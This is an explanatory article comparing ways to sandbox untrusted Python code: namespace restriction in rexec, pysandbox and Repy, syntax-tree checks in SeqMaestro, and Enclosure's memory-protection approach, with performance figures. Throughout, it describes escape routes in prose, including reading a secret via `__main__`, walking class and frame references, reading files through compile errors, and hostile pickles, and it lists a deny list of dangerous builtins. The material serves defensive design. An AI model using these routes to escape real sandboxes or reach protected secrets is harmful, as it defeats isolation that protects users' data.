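# Sandboxing untrusted code by the function or by the whole interpreter

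## What a sandbox separates, and at what size

A sandbox lets a computer run untrusted code while limiting what that code can read, change or contact. Web browsers use sandboxes to run scripts from web pages, and cloud companies use them to run many customers' programs on one machine. More recently, AI coding agents, in which a language model writes commands and a computer executes them, have begun running a lot of code that nobody reviews first. *SideKernel* (2026), a paper about a sandbox for such agents on Apple computers, lists some of the risks: hostile text can hijack the agent, private data can leak, and the agent can install malware because the model made up the name of a software package.

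A sandbox can enclose one function of a program, or even one call to that function, while everything else runs outside. It can also enclose a whole language interpreter and every library the interpreter has loaded. For a language like Python, the smaller sandbox is much harder to build than it sounds.

### A parser next to a key

For example, a Python program might issue signed receipts and keep its secret signing key in a global variable. Customers upload order files in an odd format, which the program reads by calling `parse`, a script from an outside source (a contractor, a stranger on the internet or a language model).

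```python
SIGNING_KEY = load_key()

def handle(upload):
    orders = parse(upload)        # untrusted
    return sign(orders, SIGNING_KEY)
```

The script should receive the bytes of one file and return a list of orders. It doesn't need access to the key, the disk or the network. The script may be malicious, or it may have a bug that lets a malicious file take control of it. Both cases require the same defense, because either way the attacker gains access to whatever `parse` can reach.

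In ordinary Python, `parse` can reach the key with `import __main__` and then `__main__.SIGNING_KEY`. Blocking that route adds little protection, because the interpreter has many others.

### What one interpreter holds

A program called an interpreter executes Python code. The standard one is CPython, which is written in C. Programmers also use "interpreter" to mean the state that this program keeps while it runs. *PEP 734* (Snow, 2023), a design proposal for Python's standard library, defines an interpreter in this second sense as essentially all the runtime state that Python threads (lines of execution within a running program) must share. One copy of this state is an interpreter instance, and most Python programs have exactly one.

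The largest part of it is the heap, the region of memory where objects live. According to the Python documentation's *Memory Management* page, a single private heap contains all Python objects, and the interpreter alone manages it. A function can't have a part of the heap to itself. CPython packs small objects (512 bytes or less) into blocks of 1 MiB on 64-bit machines, so the signing key and a string that `parse` has just created can be adjacent. Processors usually protect memory in pages of 4 KiB or more, so hardware can't isolate the key without also isolating the other objects on its page, unless somebody first changes how CPython allocates memory.

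The module table, `sys.modules`, lists every module the program has imported. When `parse` imports a module that the host already uses, it gets the same module object and can replace one of the module's functions with its own version, which the host would then call.

Each object also carries a reference count, the number of places that point to it. CPython raises the count when a new variable points to the object, lowers it when one goes away, and frees the object at zero. Python's developers put the principle bluntly in an old edition of the Python documentation: code owns references, never objects, and "objects are always shared". There is an awkward consequence for sandboxing, which is that *reading* an object usually means *writing* to its memory, because the count changes. A host that wants to lend `parse` a lookup table in read-only memory will find that the interpreter itself trips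 over the restriction. (CPython now exempts some built-in objects, such as `None` and small integers, by fixing their counts.)

Reference counts miss groups of objects that point only to one another, so a garbage collector looks for those. It has to track objects across the whole instance, and any code can read its records. Schemenauer's *gc* describes the function `gc.get_objects()`, which returns a list of every object the collector tracks. The list would include the dictionary of global variables that contains the key, but not the key itself, since the collector generally skips simple values like byte strings.

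Finally, there are native extensions, which the Python documentation's *Introduction* to the C interface defines as C modules that extend the interpreter. Much of Python's numerical software uses them. An extension runs as machine code and can access all the memory of its process, which is a running program with its own address space. Python's rules about names and attributes don't apply to the extension.

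Two Python functions in one instance normally share the same memory, modules and permissions, because a function is a way of organizing source code and has none of these of its own.

### Why a second interpreter is not enough

CPython has allowed several interpreter instances in one process since 1997, and Python 3.14 made the feature available from Python code. Moving `parse` into a second instance gives it its own modules, classes, functions and variables, so `import __main__` now finds a different `__main__`. Each instance also has its own garbage collector state (Snow, 2022, *PEP 684*).

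But the two instances still share the process's memory, open files and environment variables. If the program loaded the key from an environment variable, `parse` can read it there. Code in one instance can also call `os.close()` and close a file that the other has open, as the Python documentation's *Multiple interpreters in a Python process* notes. Native extensions can access everything in the process. The documentation's *concurrent.interpreters* page therefore tells readers not to use multiple interpreters in security-sensitive situations.

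Even the return value can be unsafe. Most objects pass between instances through pickle, Python's format for turning objects into bytes and back, and rebuilding an object from a pickle can execute code that the sender chose. A hostile `parse` could return a supposed list of orders that runs commands in the host when the host rebuilds it.

An interpreter instance is convenient to sandbox because it holds the state that functions share, but a separate mechanism has to enforce the isolation.

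### Terms for the two sides

Researchers have long used incompatible terms for such boundaries. In *SoK: Software Compartmentalization*, Lefeuvre, Dautenhahn and colleagues (2024) argue that this is partly why compartmentalization, or splitting a large program into parts with limited privileges, has been adopted slowly. They propose a single model for comparing designs. The model's basic unit is the protection domain, a body of code or execution that shares one set of permissions. Without a sandbox, the receipt program is a single domain.

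With a sandbox there are at least two. The *host* is the trusted program that runs the untrusted code and owns the key. The *guest* is the untrusted code and any runtime inside the sandbox with it. A *policy* specifies which memory, files, network addresses and host services the guest may use. The policy for `parse` could be very short, allowing it only to read the given bytes and return a list.

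A *crossing* is a transfer of control across the boundary in either direction, so a call to `parse` and its return make two crossings. If `parse` calls back into the host to look up an exchange rate, that call and its return add two more. The *interface surface* is everything through which the two sides can affect each other. It includes the arguments, the return value, the exchange-rate lookup, any shared memory, and any system calls the guest may make (requests to the operating system's kernel, such as to open a file).

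The *trusted computing base* is the code and hardware that must be correct for the sandbox to hold. It usually includes CPython when the sandbox separates two functions in one Python instance, so a memory bug in CPython can let an attacker cross the boundary. When the sandbox encloses a whole interpreter, the CPython inside is part of the guest. An attacker who takes it over gains only the access that the policy already allowed, and must still break the mechanism that enforces the boundary to get out.

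Lefeuvre and colleagues also distinguish two kinds of boundary. A code-centric boundary goes around a piece of code, so `parse` has few permissions no matter who calls it or on what file. A data-centric boundary goes around a run of execution, so the same code can run in different domains depending on whose data it is handling. Some designs combine the two. If a rival of one customer uploads a malicious file, a code-centric sandbox protects the key. But if `parse` keeps its memory from one upload to the next, the file may be able to read the previous customer's orders. A fresh domain for each call prevents that. "Per-function sandbox" can mean either kind, and the difference matters once a program has more than one user.

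Then there is the question of who distrusts whom. Lefeuvre and colleagues distinguish three trust models:

- In the *sandbox* model, the enclosed part is the suspect and the rest of the program needs protection from it. A parser for untrusted files is a standard case.
- In the *safebox* model, the enclosed part is the valuable one, such as a secret key and the code that uses it, and the rest of the program is the suspect.
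- Under *mutual distrust*, neither side may read the other's private data.

The receipt program could use any of them. A safebox around the key would protect it from bugs in every other part of the program, which a sandbox around `parse` does not do. But it would leave `parse` free to read the disk and use the network. `parse` could also still use the safebox to sign a forged receipt, which would make the safebox a confused deputy, a trusted component that an attacker gets to misuse its permissions.

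Lefeuvre and colleagues exclude whole-program sandboxes and virtual machines from their definition of compartmentalization, although both follow the sandbox trust model. Their terms still apply when the sandbox contains a complete interpreter.

### From one call to a whole machine

| Size of sandbox | What goes inside, for the receipt program |
|---|---|
| Single call | One run of `parse` on one upload |
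| Function | `parse`, for all uploads |
| Library | `parse` and the package of helper code it came with |
| Interpreter instance | A separate copy of Python, with its own heap and modules, running `parse` |
| Process | That copy of Python plus its address space, C libraries and open files |
| Virtual machine | Usually all of the above plus an operating system kernel |

The rows don't nest perfectly. Several interpreter instances can share a process, or one can have a process to itself. Agent builders face the same choice with skills, the reusable routines that language-model agents load. *SoK: Agentic Skills* (2026), a survey of these routines, treats granularity as the key question in sandboxing them, namely whether each skill should get its own sandbox, all skills in a session should share one, or the arrangement should vary with how far the operator trusts the skill.

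People often sort sandboxes by mechanism instead. *SideKernel* has three classes: those that share the host's kernel, those that rely on a language runtime, and those that give each workload its own kernel through virtualization, a processor feature that lets a guest run as if it had a machine to itself. This classification helps in judging how hard a sandbox is to break out of, but it doesn't specify what the sandbox encloses. Virtualization most often encloses an entire operating system, but the survey by Lefeuvre and colleagues also includes virtual machines that hold one component of a kernel and others, called virtines, that hold one function.

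In *Software Compartmentalization Trade-Offs with Hardware Capabilities*, Kressel, Lefeuvre and Olivier (2023) used one mechanism to isolate both functions and libraries, working with the database SQLite and the cryptography library LibSodium. They used Arm's experimental Morello processor, which supports *capabilities*, pointers with bounds and permissions that the hardware checks at each access. In their first method, programmers replace each pointer that enters the sandbox with a capability by hand. The guest can then access only the exact bytes the host shares with it, and the number of sandboxes can grow without limit. But programmers have to rewrite more code as the compartment gets bigger, and Kressel and colleagues suggest that the method may suit only one or a few functions. In their second method, the two sides share a region of memory, and programmers only have to mark the shared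 data and the calls between compartments. This takes far less work, but it leaves the entire region open to both sides all the time and doesn't scale beyond a couple of compartments.

So the same hardware works at either size, though the size affects how much work a given method takes. Sometimes the mechanism forces the choice. WebAssembly, a portable instruction format whose code can reach the outside only through functions the host provides, can hold a single function written in a language like C. A Python function needs an interpreter, so the interpreter has to go into WebAssembly with it (shayon.dev, *Let's discuss sandbox isolation*, 2026).

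### What depends on the size

A small boundary allows a more specific policy. A sandbox around `parse` alone can deny all file access. A sandbox around a Python process must let the interpreter read its standard library from disk, and `parse` inherits that permission. If the sandbox contains the entire receipt program, no policy can keep the key from `parse`, because both are in the same domain. The policy can only limit where the key goes afterwards, but that is still useful. The overview on shayon.dev stresses that even the strongest virtual machine is little help if code inside it can read a secret and has unrestricted network access.

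Smaller sandboxes tend to have wider interfaces, however. A function call inside a program passes live objects, and each can lead to others. If `handle` passes `parse` an upload object that points to the customer's session, the session is part of the interface. Lefeuvre, Bădoiu and colleagues, in *Assessing the impact of interface vulnerabilities in compartmentalized software*, study the bugs that appear when a call that used to come from a trusted component may now be an attack. A sandbox around a separate interpreter can exchange only bytes with the code outside, which is much easier to check, but its designer has to build it that way. An ordinary Linux process can make roughly 340 kinds of system call, by the count on shayon.dev, and the default filter of Docker, a popular container system, still allows about 300.

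The third consideration is communication overhead. Two functions in one instance pass a reference and copy nothing. Across most larger boundaries, the program has to marshal its data, which means converting arguments and results into a form it can copy over, and it may also have to start the sandbox first. Wang and Zheng (2026) measured about 5 milliseconds of extra startup time for *Sandlock*, a process-sized sandbox for agents' code. Nobody will notice that delay once per upload, but a program that started a fresh sandbox for each line of a 10,000-line file would spend 50 seconds on the extra startup time alone. Such overhead is a good part of why programmers kept trying to restrict Python code from inside the interpreter, despite a poor record.

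## Restricting code inside a shared Python interpreter: pysandbox and Repy

The cheapest sandbox for a Python function runs the guest in the host's own interpreter and withholds most of the language from it. Python's built-in function `exec` runs source code, and its caller can choose the dictionary where that code looks up global names. The receipt program could load the untrusted script this way:

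```python
allowed = {"len": len, "range": range, "int": int}
scope = {"__builtins__": allowed}
exec(script, scope)               # defines parse
orders = scope["parse"](upload)
```

Normally `__builtins__` gives code access to functions such as `open` and the function behind `import`, but here it holds only three harmless ones. `SIGNING_KEY` isn't in `scope`, and `import __main__` now fails. A careful host would also inspect the script before running it. Python can parse the source into a syntax tree, a nested description of every statement and expression, and the host can refuse any script whose tree contains an import or a suspicious name.

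After that, calling `parse` has no more overhead than calling any other Python function, and the method works on every operating system. The policy is a list of names, which the host can make arbitrarily short.

Python once included a sandbox of this kind, called `rexec`. The Python documentation's *Restricted Execution* page describes a trusted supervisor that runs untrusted code in a "padded cell" with limited permissions. A later redesign of Python's classes introduced security holes, and the developers disabled the module in Python 2.3. The Python documentation's *rexec* page advises against relying on it in production and suggests separate processes as one alternative.

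### How an ordinary object leads to a hidden one

The dictionary limits the names that `parse` can use, but code can also reach an object without naming it, by following references from another object. Every Python value refers to its class, and every class refers to the classes it inherits from. These chains all end at `object`, which keeps a list of the classes directly below it. A guest that holds only an empty tuple can therefore go up from the tuple to `object` and back down to classes from all over the program. Ned Batchelder, in *Eval really is dangerous*, shows that this works even after the host has removed every global variable and every built-in function. What the guest finds depends on what the program has loaded, which is usually a lot in a real program.

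While a function runs, the interpreter keeps a frame that records its local variables and refers to the caller's frame. Exceptions give code access to frames because Python uses the frames to print where an error happened. In the receipt program, `handle` calls `parse`, so the frame of `handle` is one step away from the guest, and it refers to the global variables, which include the signing key.

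Objects passed between the host and the guest are another problem. David Wheeler points out in *Python*, part of his guide to secure programming, that Python passes most objects by reference, so a guest that receives a list can change the host's own list. He recommends copying anything changeable. He also notes that Python automatically calls many "hidden" methods on objects. If `parse` returns orders that belong to a class it defined, `sign` may run the guest's code just by comparing two of them.

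A host can forbid the attributes that make up these paths, such as an object's link to its class. However, the syntax tree shows only the attribute names that appear in the source. Some functions and string formatting can look up an attribute at run time from a name given as a string.

In 2016 the programmer Jon Ribbens invited Python's developers to break a sandbox that anticipated much of this. According to Ribbens (2016), in *Challenge*, it refused all names beginning with an underscore, along with a few others, and banned the `with` statement. It offered no imports, since the guest might alter a module that the host was also using, and it replaced the function that looks up attributes by string. Stinner (2016), in *Challenge*, broke the sandbox through trusted library code that still had the original lookup function, using that code as a confused deputy to fetch a hidden attribute for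 the guest.

### Three years of pysandbox

Victor Stinner, a CPython developer, knew where to look because he had already spent three years on his own sandbox, pysandbox. *The pysandbox project is broken* (Stinner, 2013) explains how it failed.

A developer known as Tav wrote a small sandbox that hid sensitive attributes and challenged Python's core developers to break it. They quickly did. Stinner thought the idea could work with more protections, and he released pysandbox 1.0 in June 2010. It ran untrusted code in a new, empty namespace. *Python jails* (Stinner, 2011) says that pysandbox used an allow-list for built-in functions but a block-list for object attributes. A block-list is weaker because it covers only the dangers its author has thought of.

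An early use of pysandbox was a bot on a French chat channel about Python. It ran whatever code people sent it, and most of them were trying to break out of the sandbox. Three months after the release, somebody found that sandboxed code could modify the dictionary of built-in functions and so tamper with the sandbox's own functions. Stinner would have preferred to use a special protected type for the built-ins, but CPython's C code required a real dictionary. So he blocked the ordinary ways of removing a key from *any* dictionary. Then somebody found another dictionary method that allowed the same tampering, and he blocked that too.

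Seven months later, he removed the time limit on guest code because it couldn't interrupt a long computation inside a C function. He also blocked an attribute that let the guest crash the interpreter, but had to leave it accessible on Python 2.5 because of a different CPython bug.

In 2013, participants in a security challenge found two more vulnerabilities in less than a day. One let an attacker follow the frames from an exception to the host's global variables. The other involved `compile`, a function that translates source code. Python displays the offending line when it reports a syntax error, which let the attacker read any file on the disk, one line at a time.

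Stinner fixed both, but he regarded the `compile` bug as proof that nobody could put a sandbox inside CPython. Blocking `open` doesn't prevent file access if an unrelated function reads files as a side effect. The policy for `parse` denies file access in one line, but a host that restricts names has to find every function in the interpreter that might open a file.

He also complained that pysandbox had become impractical for anything more complicated than evaluating `1+(2*3)`. Guest code couldn't delete a key from a dictionary, and the host couldn't pass it arbitrary objects. Individual protections couldn't be turned off because the sandbox needed all of them.

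Stinner had hoped to merge pysandbox into CPython and proposed a read-only dictionary type as a step towards that, but the other developers rejected it. He ended up recommending that people run the whole Python process inside an external sandbox. The pysandbox repository now includes the same advice, "run python in a sandbox, not the opposite!"

### The C code underneath

Even a perfect block-list would leave the interpreter in the trusted computing base. Stinner counted more than 126,000 lines of C in just two directories of the CPython 3.4 source, and a single bug in them could let untrusted code escape. In the 2016 discussion he added that the string type alone, which any useful sandbox has to allow, has about 20,000 lines.

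D'Aprano (2016), in *Challenge*, thought this argument proved too much. A guest can call only the 44 public methods of a string, not arbitrary lines of C. If a method only returns true or false, the guest can't get a hidden namespace out of it, whatever its C code does internally. So Ribbens could audit what the 44 methods return instead of auditing 20,000 lines of C.

This seems right as long as the C code works correctly and the audit is a good one. `format` is one of the 44, and Stinner had found within minutes that it could look up an object's class. But D'Aprano himself made an exception for bugs that crash the interpreter and might let the guest run arbitrary machine code, and that exception is large. *The pysandbox project is broken* (Fijalkowski, 2013) quotes a 2013 message in which the CPython developer Nick Coghlan argued that it is reasonable to treat any such crash as a security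 hole, and that CPython was still far from impossible to crash with ordinary Python code. Coghlan added that sandboxing inside a process is hard even for Lua, JavaScript and Java, whose designers had it in mind from the start.

Restricting names also does little to limit memory and time use. In a thread on the Python developers' forum, *Extending subinterpreters with sandboxing capabilities*, one reply describes a two-line loop that keeps doubling the length of a list. It uses only `range` and `list`, which almost any policy would allow. Several people in the thread had tried to build such sandboxes themselves and told the newcomer not to. *The Python Programming Language*, by the developers of the Linux distribution Fedora, calls standard CPython unsuitable for sandboxing.

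### Repy and its layers

Cappos, Dadgar and colleagues (2010), in *Retaining Sandbox Containment Despite Bugs in Privileged Memory-Safe Code*, got further by giving up most of Python's flexibility from the start. Their language, Repy, is a subset of Python 2.5.4. They built it for a network testbed where researchers ran experiments on thousands of computers lent by volunteers, so the sandbox had to keep the researchers' programs away from the rest of each volunteer's machine.

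They were mainly worried about bugs in standard libraries. In Java 1.4.2, for example, the code that rebuilt a calendar object from stored bytes could create an object of a broader type than the programmers intended. An attacker could use that to load a new security policy and gain every permission. Although the bug was in ordinary Java code rather than C, it broke the whole sandbox because the library ran with full privileges.

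In Repy, only a small *sandbox kernel* has such privileges. It is a Python program, unrelated to the operating system's kernel. It offers 32 operations, including 13 for the network and 6 for files in one dedicated directory. It can also check source code and run it in a fresh namespace with only the operations the caller lists. Most other library code, including the code for XML, cryptography and web requests, runs without special privileges. Even `import` is a library function that reads a file and passes the text to the sandbox kernel.

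The machine's owner can insert *security layers* between the kernel and the user's program. Each layer starts the next one up and determines which functions it receives. One real layer kept a log of an experiment's actions that the experimenter wasn't supposed to alter. It received the kernel's functions for opening and deleting files and passed up its own versions, which protected the log. The experimenter's program had no reference to the originals.

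The program has to trust the logging layer, because its file operations go through that layer, but the layer doesn't trust the program, and the kernel trusts neither. A bug in the logging layer might let the program delete the log, but the program still couldn't do anything that the kernel hadn't allowed the layer to do.

Separate namespaces alone would not be enough for this, since two layers could still share objects. Cappos and colleagues wrote an *encasement library* that wraps every function one layer offers another. A contract lists the function's argument and result types and the exceptions it may raise, and the library terminates the program if a call breaks the contract. The library also copies mutable arguments and results. Otherwise a program could pass a list of harmless file names, wait for the layer to check it, and swap in other names before the layer used it.

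All of this assumes that code can use only what it has been given. Computer scientists call a language that guarantees this an object-capability language, and ordinary Python isn't one, for the reasons above. If a Repy program could reach the kernel's functions from an empty tuple, the layers in between would be pointless. So the sandbox checks the program's syntax tree and accepts only listed constructs, which rules out, for example, classes that inherit from basic types or manage their own attribute storage. The program gets 87 built-in items, 53 of which are constants and exceptions. If it calls a built-in function for inspecting other objects, the sandbox terminates it. Designers can go further by writing a new interpreter for a small subset of Python, which also removes CPython from the trusted code.

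Cappos and colleagues evaluated the design by asking what each mistake in a published list of Java vulnerabilities would have done in the corresponding part of Repy. Three of the researchers rated the bugs independently and then settled their disagreements. They concluded that Repy's layers would likely have stopped at least six of the eight applicable bugs that had let attackers run arbitrary code. The reports on the other two contained too little detail to judge.

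This is decent evidence about library bugs, though it rests on the designers' own judgment rather than on attacks against Repy. The "six of eight" figure also excludes another six bugs on the list that allowed arbitrary code execution, all of them in the component that checks Java's compiled code. The team left these out because they couldn't translate them to Repy, but layers can't contain bugs at that depth. Repy takes a lot of library code out of the trusted computing base but leaves CPython in it, and Cappos and colleagues acknowledge that a flaw in Python's memory safety or type conversion would let an attacker run arbitrary code in their sandbox as well.

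The layers added little overhead. A call from one layer to another took between 6 and 15 microseconds on a desktop computer of the time, depending on the arguments. Calls with immutable arguments, such as strings, took 12 microseconds, so one call for each line of a 10,000-line file would add 0.12 seconds. A call between two local processes through XML-RPC, a common protocol, took about a thousand times as long as a call between layers. A version with checks prepared in advance needed less than 2 microseconds per call, but the team didn't deploy it because its correctness was harder to verify. Starting the sandbox and the encasement library took about 173 milliseconds, and each further layer added 2.5 milliseconds.

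### Checking functions that a language model wrote

People still use this design, now for code from language models. *SeqMaestro* (Saveliev, Kacprzyk and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that searches DNA and RNA sequences for properties that predict a biological outcome. A language model proposes each property as a short Python function, such as one that counts how often the base C comes directly before G. The system runs each function on the user's sequences and tests how well the result predicts the outcome. The prompts contain rows of the user's data, so an attacker could plant instructions in a data file and get the model to write harmful code.

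Before running a function, SeqMaestro inspects its syntax tree. It allows imports only from a short list and rejects attribute names that begin with a double underscore, references to `open`, `eval`, `exec`, `compile` and `getattr`, and any code outside a function definition except imports. It then compiles the tree it inspected instead of reading the text again, so the code it runs can't differ from the code it checked. It runs the function with a minimal set of built-ins and a restricted import mechanism.

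Saveliev and colleagues write that the checks make accidental or casual misuse difficult, but that only isolating the process, which they have not attempted, stops a patient adversary. The checks also cover only one route from a malicious data file to the machine. In the runs they report, a separate AI agent with access to a shell and the file system directed the analysis.

This may be enough protection for a tool that biologists run on their own data, because most bad code from a language model is wrong rather than hostile. The model may import a package that the host hasn't approved, try to open a file, or leave test code outside its functions, and a syntax check catches all of these before anything runs. SeqMaestro discards and counts the rejected functions, so when a prompt starts to produce unusable code, the number of candidates visibly falls. A host could also send the model the reason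 for a rejection and ask it to try again.

Real Python's *eval()* page discusses a small calculator that removes the built-ins and rejects any expression containing a name. It likewise recommends this pattern as protection against accidents, not as a sandbox for untrusted input. In 2026, Python's developers added a warning to the Python documentation that overriding `__builtins__` is not a security mechanism.

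Coghlan called a sandbox at the language level "at best, a first line of defence" against naive attacks, and thought its designers should plan for someone getting through. Inside a process sandbox, a syntax check can still save time and filter out crude attacks, and an attacker who gets past it must then escape the process sandbox. The receipt program has no second barrier, and its signing key is in the same memory as `parse`. Protecting the key there requires a mechanism below the language, such as the processor's control over which memory a function may access.

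## Restricting memory for one function call: Enclosures in Go and Python

A processor checks every memory access against a table of permissions, whatever language the program is written in. Normally one table covers a whole process. In 2021, Ghosn, Kogias and colleagues, in *Enclosure*, used these checks to give a single function call access to less memory than the rest of the program has. They built a full version for Go, a compiled language, and a prototype for Python. The Go version adds little overhead to many programs. With the Python version, a program that drew a chart took about 18 times as long as usual because of the way CPython stores objects.

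The team worried mainly about libraries. A short program may import one package that pulls in hundreds of others from unknown developers, and all of them run with the program's full permissions. Attackers have exploited this, for example with Python packages that stole login keys from the disk.

### What an enclosure restricts

A closure is a function together with the variables it uses from the surrounding code. An *enclosure* is a closure with two restrictions permanently attached. One is a *memory view*, which specifies the packages whose code and data the closure may use. The other is a filter for system calls, which are grouped into categories such as `net` for the network and `file` for files.

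Packages work as units of memory because each one owns its functions, constants and global variables, plus an *arena*, the part of the heap where its functions create objects. A developer can let the closure only read a package (`R`), read and write it (`RW`), or read it, write it and call its functions (`RWX`). `U` removes a package from the closure's view.

In a notation close to the paper's, the receipt program could wrap its parser like this:

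```
safe_parse = with [uploads: R, none] func(upload) {
    return parse(upload)
}
```

This assumes that the host keeps uploaded files in a separate package called `uploads`. The guest can read that package but can't access the main program or its signing key, and `none` forbids all system calls. The policy doesn't need to mention the parser's own package, because an enclosure starts with access to everything its closure imports, directly or through other packages. Ghosn and colleagues chose this default so that developers wouldn't have to list every indirect import. Such a list would take a lot of work to write and could break with the next update.

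When `handle` calls `safe_parse`, a runtime component called LitterBox switches to the restricted view, and it switches back when the closure returns. Everything that runs in between has the same restrictions, including helper packages and machine code from unsafe languages. In Go, a thread that the guest starts inherits them too. One enclosure can call another, but the inner one can't have any permission that the outer one lacks. The parser's developer could restrict a decompression library further, but couldn't give it network access that the host had denied.

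If the guest breaks a rule, LitterBox aborts the whole program. The key stays safe, but one bad upload can stop the service for every customer.

The same package can run under different policies in different enclosures, so this is largely what Lefeuvre and colleagues call a data-centric boundary. But each call doesn't get a fresh domain, because the parser's global variables survive from one upload to the next. The restrictions also end when the closure returns, so the host should check that the result contains only plain lists, strings and numbers. Otherwise `sign` could run one of the guest's hidden methods with full access to the key.

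### Two ways to switch views

Hardware protects memory in whole pages, so two packages with different permissions can't share one. The modified Go compiler and linker put each package that appears in an enclosure on separate pages, and the Go runtime assigns blocks of the heap to particular packages. LitterBox checks this layout when the program starts. It also keeps a list of the places in the program that may request a switch, so a guest can't get the host's view just by requesting it.

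LitterBox can enforce the views with either of two processor features. The first is memory protection keys, which Intel has supported since its Skylake processors and AMD since Zen 3. Each page of memory has a 4-bit tag that assigns it one of 16 keys. A register, a small storage slot inside the processor, holds two bits for each key, one to block all access to that key's pages and one to block writing. LitterBox switches views by writing a new value to this register, which takes about 20 nanoseconds and doesn't involve the kernel.

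Any code in the process can also write to the register. *Unlimited Lives* (2022), a paper about recovering from attacks inside a process, points out that the keys can't securely isolate anything unless other mechanisms control which code changes the register. LitterBox scans the program to make sure only its own code changes it.

Sixteen keys can be enough for a program with hundreds of packages because LitterBox groups packages that have the same permissions in every enclosure, and each group needs only one key. Ghosn and colleagues found that programs needed fewer than 16 groups in practice. For a program that needs more, they suggest the virtual keys of *libmpk* (2018), a software layer that manages protection keys.

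The second feature is VT-x, Intel's support for virtual machines. LitterBox runs the entire program in one virtual machine and acts as its operating system kernel. (Virtines, by contrast, put a single function call in a virtual machine.) LitterBox keeps a separate page table, the map from a program's addresses to memory, for each enclosure and another for the trusted code. Only kernel code can change the active page table, so the program switches by making a special system call to LitterBox, which checks where the request came from and activates a different table. But an ordinary system call, such as one to open a file, has to leave the virtual machine to reach the real Linux kernel.

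Ghosn and colleagues ran three small tests a million times each and reported the median times:

| Operation | Ordinary Go | Protection keys | VT-x |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call an empty function and return | 45 ns | 86 ns | 924 ns |
| Move four pages of memory to another package | 0 ns | 1,002 ns | 158 ns |
| Make a trivial system call | 387 ns | 523 ns | 4,126 ns |

The two crossings of an enclosure call therefore add 41 nanoseconds with protection keys and 879 with VT-x. One call for each line of a 10,000-line file would add 0.4 or 9 milliseconds, respectively. Repy needed about 120 milliseconds for the same number of calls between its layers, though on an older computer.

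The other two rows matter more for most programs. When a function creates many objects, the runtime repeatedly moves memory into its package's arena. With protection keys, Linux must change the tag on those pages each time, whereas with VT-x, LitterBox only flips bits in its own page tables. System calls are faster with protection keys, because the filter only has to look up which calls the current view allows, while with VT-x each system call that leaves the virtual machine takes about 4 microseconds. The filter requires a patched Linux kernel, because the unpatched one didn't give it access to the key register.

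### Images and web servers in Go

Both patterns showed up in real Go packages. Ghosn and colleagues wrote a 32-line program that inverts a sensitive image using Bild, an image library that brings in 166,000 lines of code. They enclosed the call to Bild with read-only access to the image and no system calls, so the library couldn't alter the image or send it anywhere. The program took 13.25 milliseconds without an enclosure, 13.91 with VT-x and 14.88 with protection keys. VT-x was faster than protection keys because Bild allocates a lot of memory and makes no system calls.

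Protection keys were much faster than VT-x for web servers. The first test used Go's standard web server and enclosed the code that answers each request, so an attacker who hijacked that code couldn't read the server's private keys. Protection keys reduced the number of requests per second by less than 2%, while VT-x reduced it by 44%. Although the enclosed code made no system calls, the trusted part of the server ran in the same virtual machine, and each system call it made had to leave that machine.

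The second test used FastHTTP, a web server library that brings in 374,000 lines of code. This time the team enclosed the server, allowed it only network calls, and left the request-handling code outside. The server couldn't call that code directly, because a nested call can't gain permissions. Instead it sent each request through a Go channel, a queue between threads, to a thread that had started outside the enclosure. Protection keys reduced requests per second by 4% and VT-x by half. VT-x did worse than in the first test because FastHTTP does less work per request but makes about as many system calls.

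These programs do little real work, so the overhead looks large. Ghosn and colleagues intended them as worst cases. They also built a small wiki that depended on 44 public packages. The web server ran in one enclosure and couldn't read the database password. The database driver ran in another and could use only its connection to the database. The wiki's slowdown was similar to FastHTTP's.

### Why Python has to write in order to read

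For the Python prototype, the team first had to change about 600 lines of CPython 3.9.1 to give each module its own memory allocator and pages, with functions stored separately from data. Python programmers don't choose where an object is stored, so the team added a function, `localcopy`, that copies an object into the memory of the module that calls it.

Python also loads modules while a program is running, so LitterBox has to extend the memory views during execution. When a guest first imports a module, LitterBox adds it to the guest's view unless the policy excludes it.

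Reference counts were a harder problem. The interpreter stores each count in a header at the start of the object, on the same page as the value. When the guest uses an object that the host has shared read-only, the interpreter tries to update the count and the hardware blocks the write. The garbage collector causes a similar problem because it keeps objects in a linked list and stores the links inside them, so adding one object can require writing to another that the guest isn't allowed to modify.

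The prototype handled each blocked update by switching to the trusted view, making the change and switching back. Using one object could therefore take four switches, two when the interpreter took a reference to it and two when it dropped the reference.

Ghosn and colleagues tested this with the popular charting library matplotlib. Their program kept sensitive data in a module named `secret` and shared it read-only with an enclosure, which drew a chart and saved it to disk. With VT-x, the program took about 18 times as long as in standard Python. It made nearly a million switches for reference counts and garbage collection. Setting up the enclosure accounted for 4.3% of the slowdown and system calls for less than 1%, so the switches account for almost all of it.

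The team doesn't report the same test with protection keys. Based on the measurements above, a million switches should take about 0.44 seconds with VT-x but only 0.02 seconds with keys, so the slowdown could have been much smaller. But a program that reads a lot of shared data would still keep making these switches, however carefully the boundary was placed.

In a second run, the team gave the enclosure write access to `secret` and turned off the switches for reference counts. The program then took only about 1.4 times as long as normal. Most of the remaining overhead came from setting up the enclosure, which happens once, so the average overhead per call would fall with more calls.

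This run simulated a better design, but only by removing part of the program's protection. The guest could read the data in both runs, and in the second it could also change the data, including the object headers, which hold each object's pointer to its class. Malicious machine code in the guest could redirect that pointer to a fake class, and the host might then run the guest's code the next time it used the object. This risk may be acceptable when the goal is only to stop a buggy library from leaking data, but not when the guest may be malicious.

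To get the speed without the write access, CPython would have to separate data from metadata. Values and class pointers would go on read-only pages, and reference counts and the garbage collector's links would go on pages the guest could write to. Ghosn and colleagues consider this the main task for future work. Even then, a guest could set one of the host's counts to zero and cause the host to free an object it was still using. Separate counts for each domain might prevent that.

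It would also be a big change to CPython. Compiled extensions contain instructions that change the count at a fixed place in the object, and Snow and Elizondo (2022) complain in *PEP 683* that this makes the memory scheme hard to alter. Ghosn and colleagues suggest that capability hardware, the kind Kressel and colleagues used, could instead protect values and counts separately without moving either.

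### Whether newer versions of Python remove the obstacle

Python's developers started working on reference counts for performance reasons, not security. Companies such as Instagram load a Python program once and then split it into many processes that share its memory. The operating system copies a shared page when a process writes to it, so updating the counts causes a lot of copying even if the program only reads. Reference counts also slow down threads that use the same object.

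To address this, Python 3.12 fixed the counts of some built-in objects, such as `None`. Python's developers call these objects *immortal*, and the garbage collector doesn't change its links in them either. A guest can therefore read them without writing to them, as an enclosure requires. But there are only a few of them, and Python code can't add more. Making a list immortal wouldn't be enough anyway, because the counts of the objects inside it would still change under Snow and Elizondo's design. Python may also write to an immortal string, to store data about it the first time a program needs that data. Extensions built for older versions of Python's stable binary interface also still write to the counts of immortal objects.

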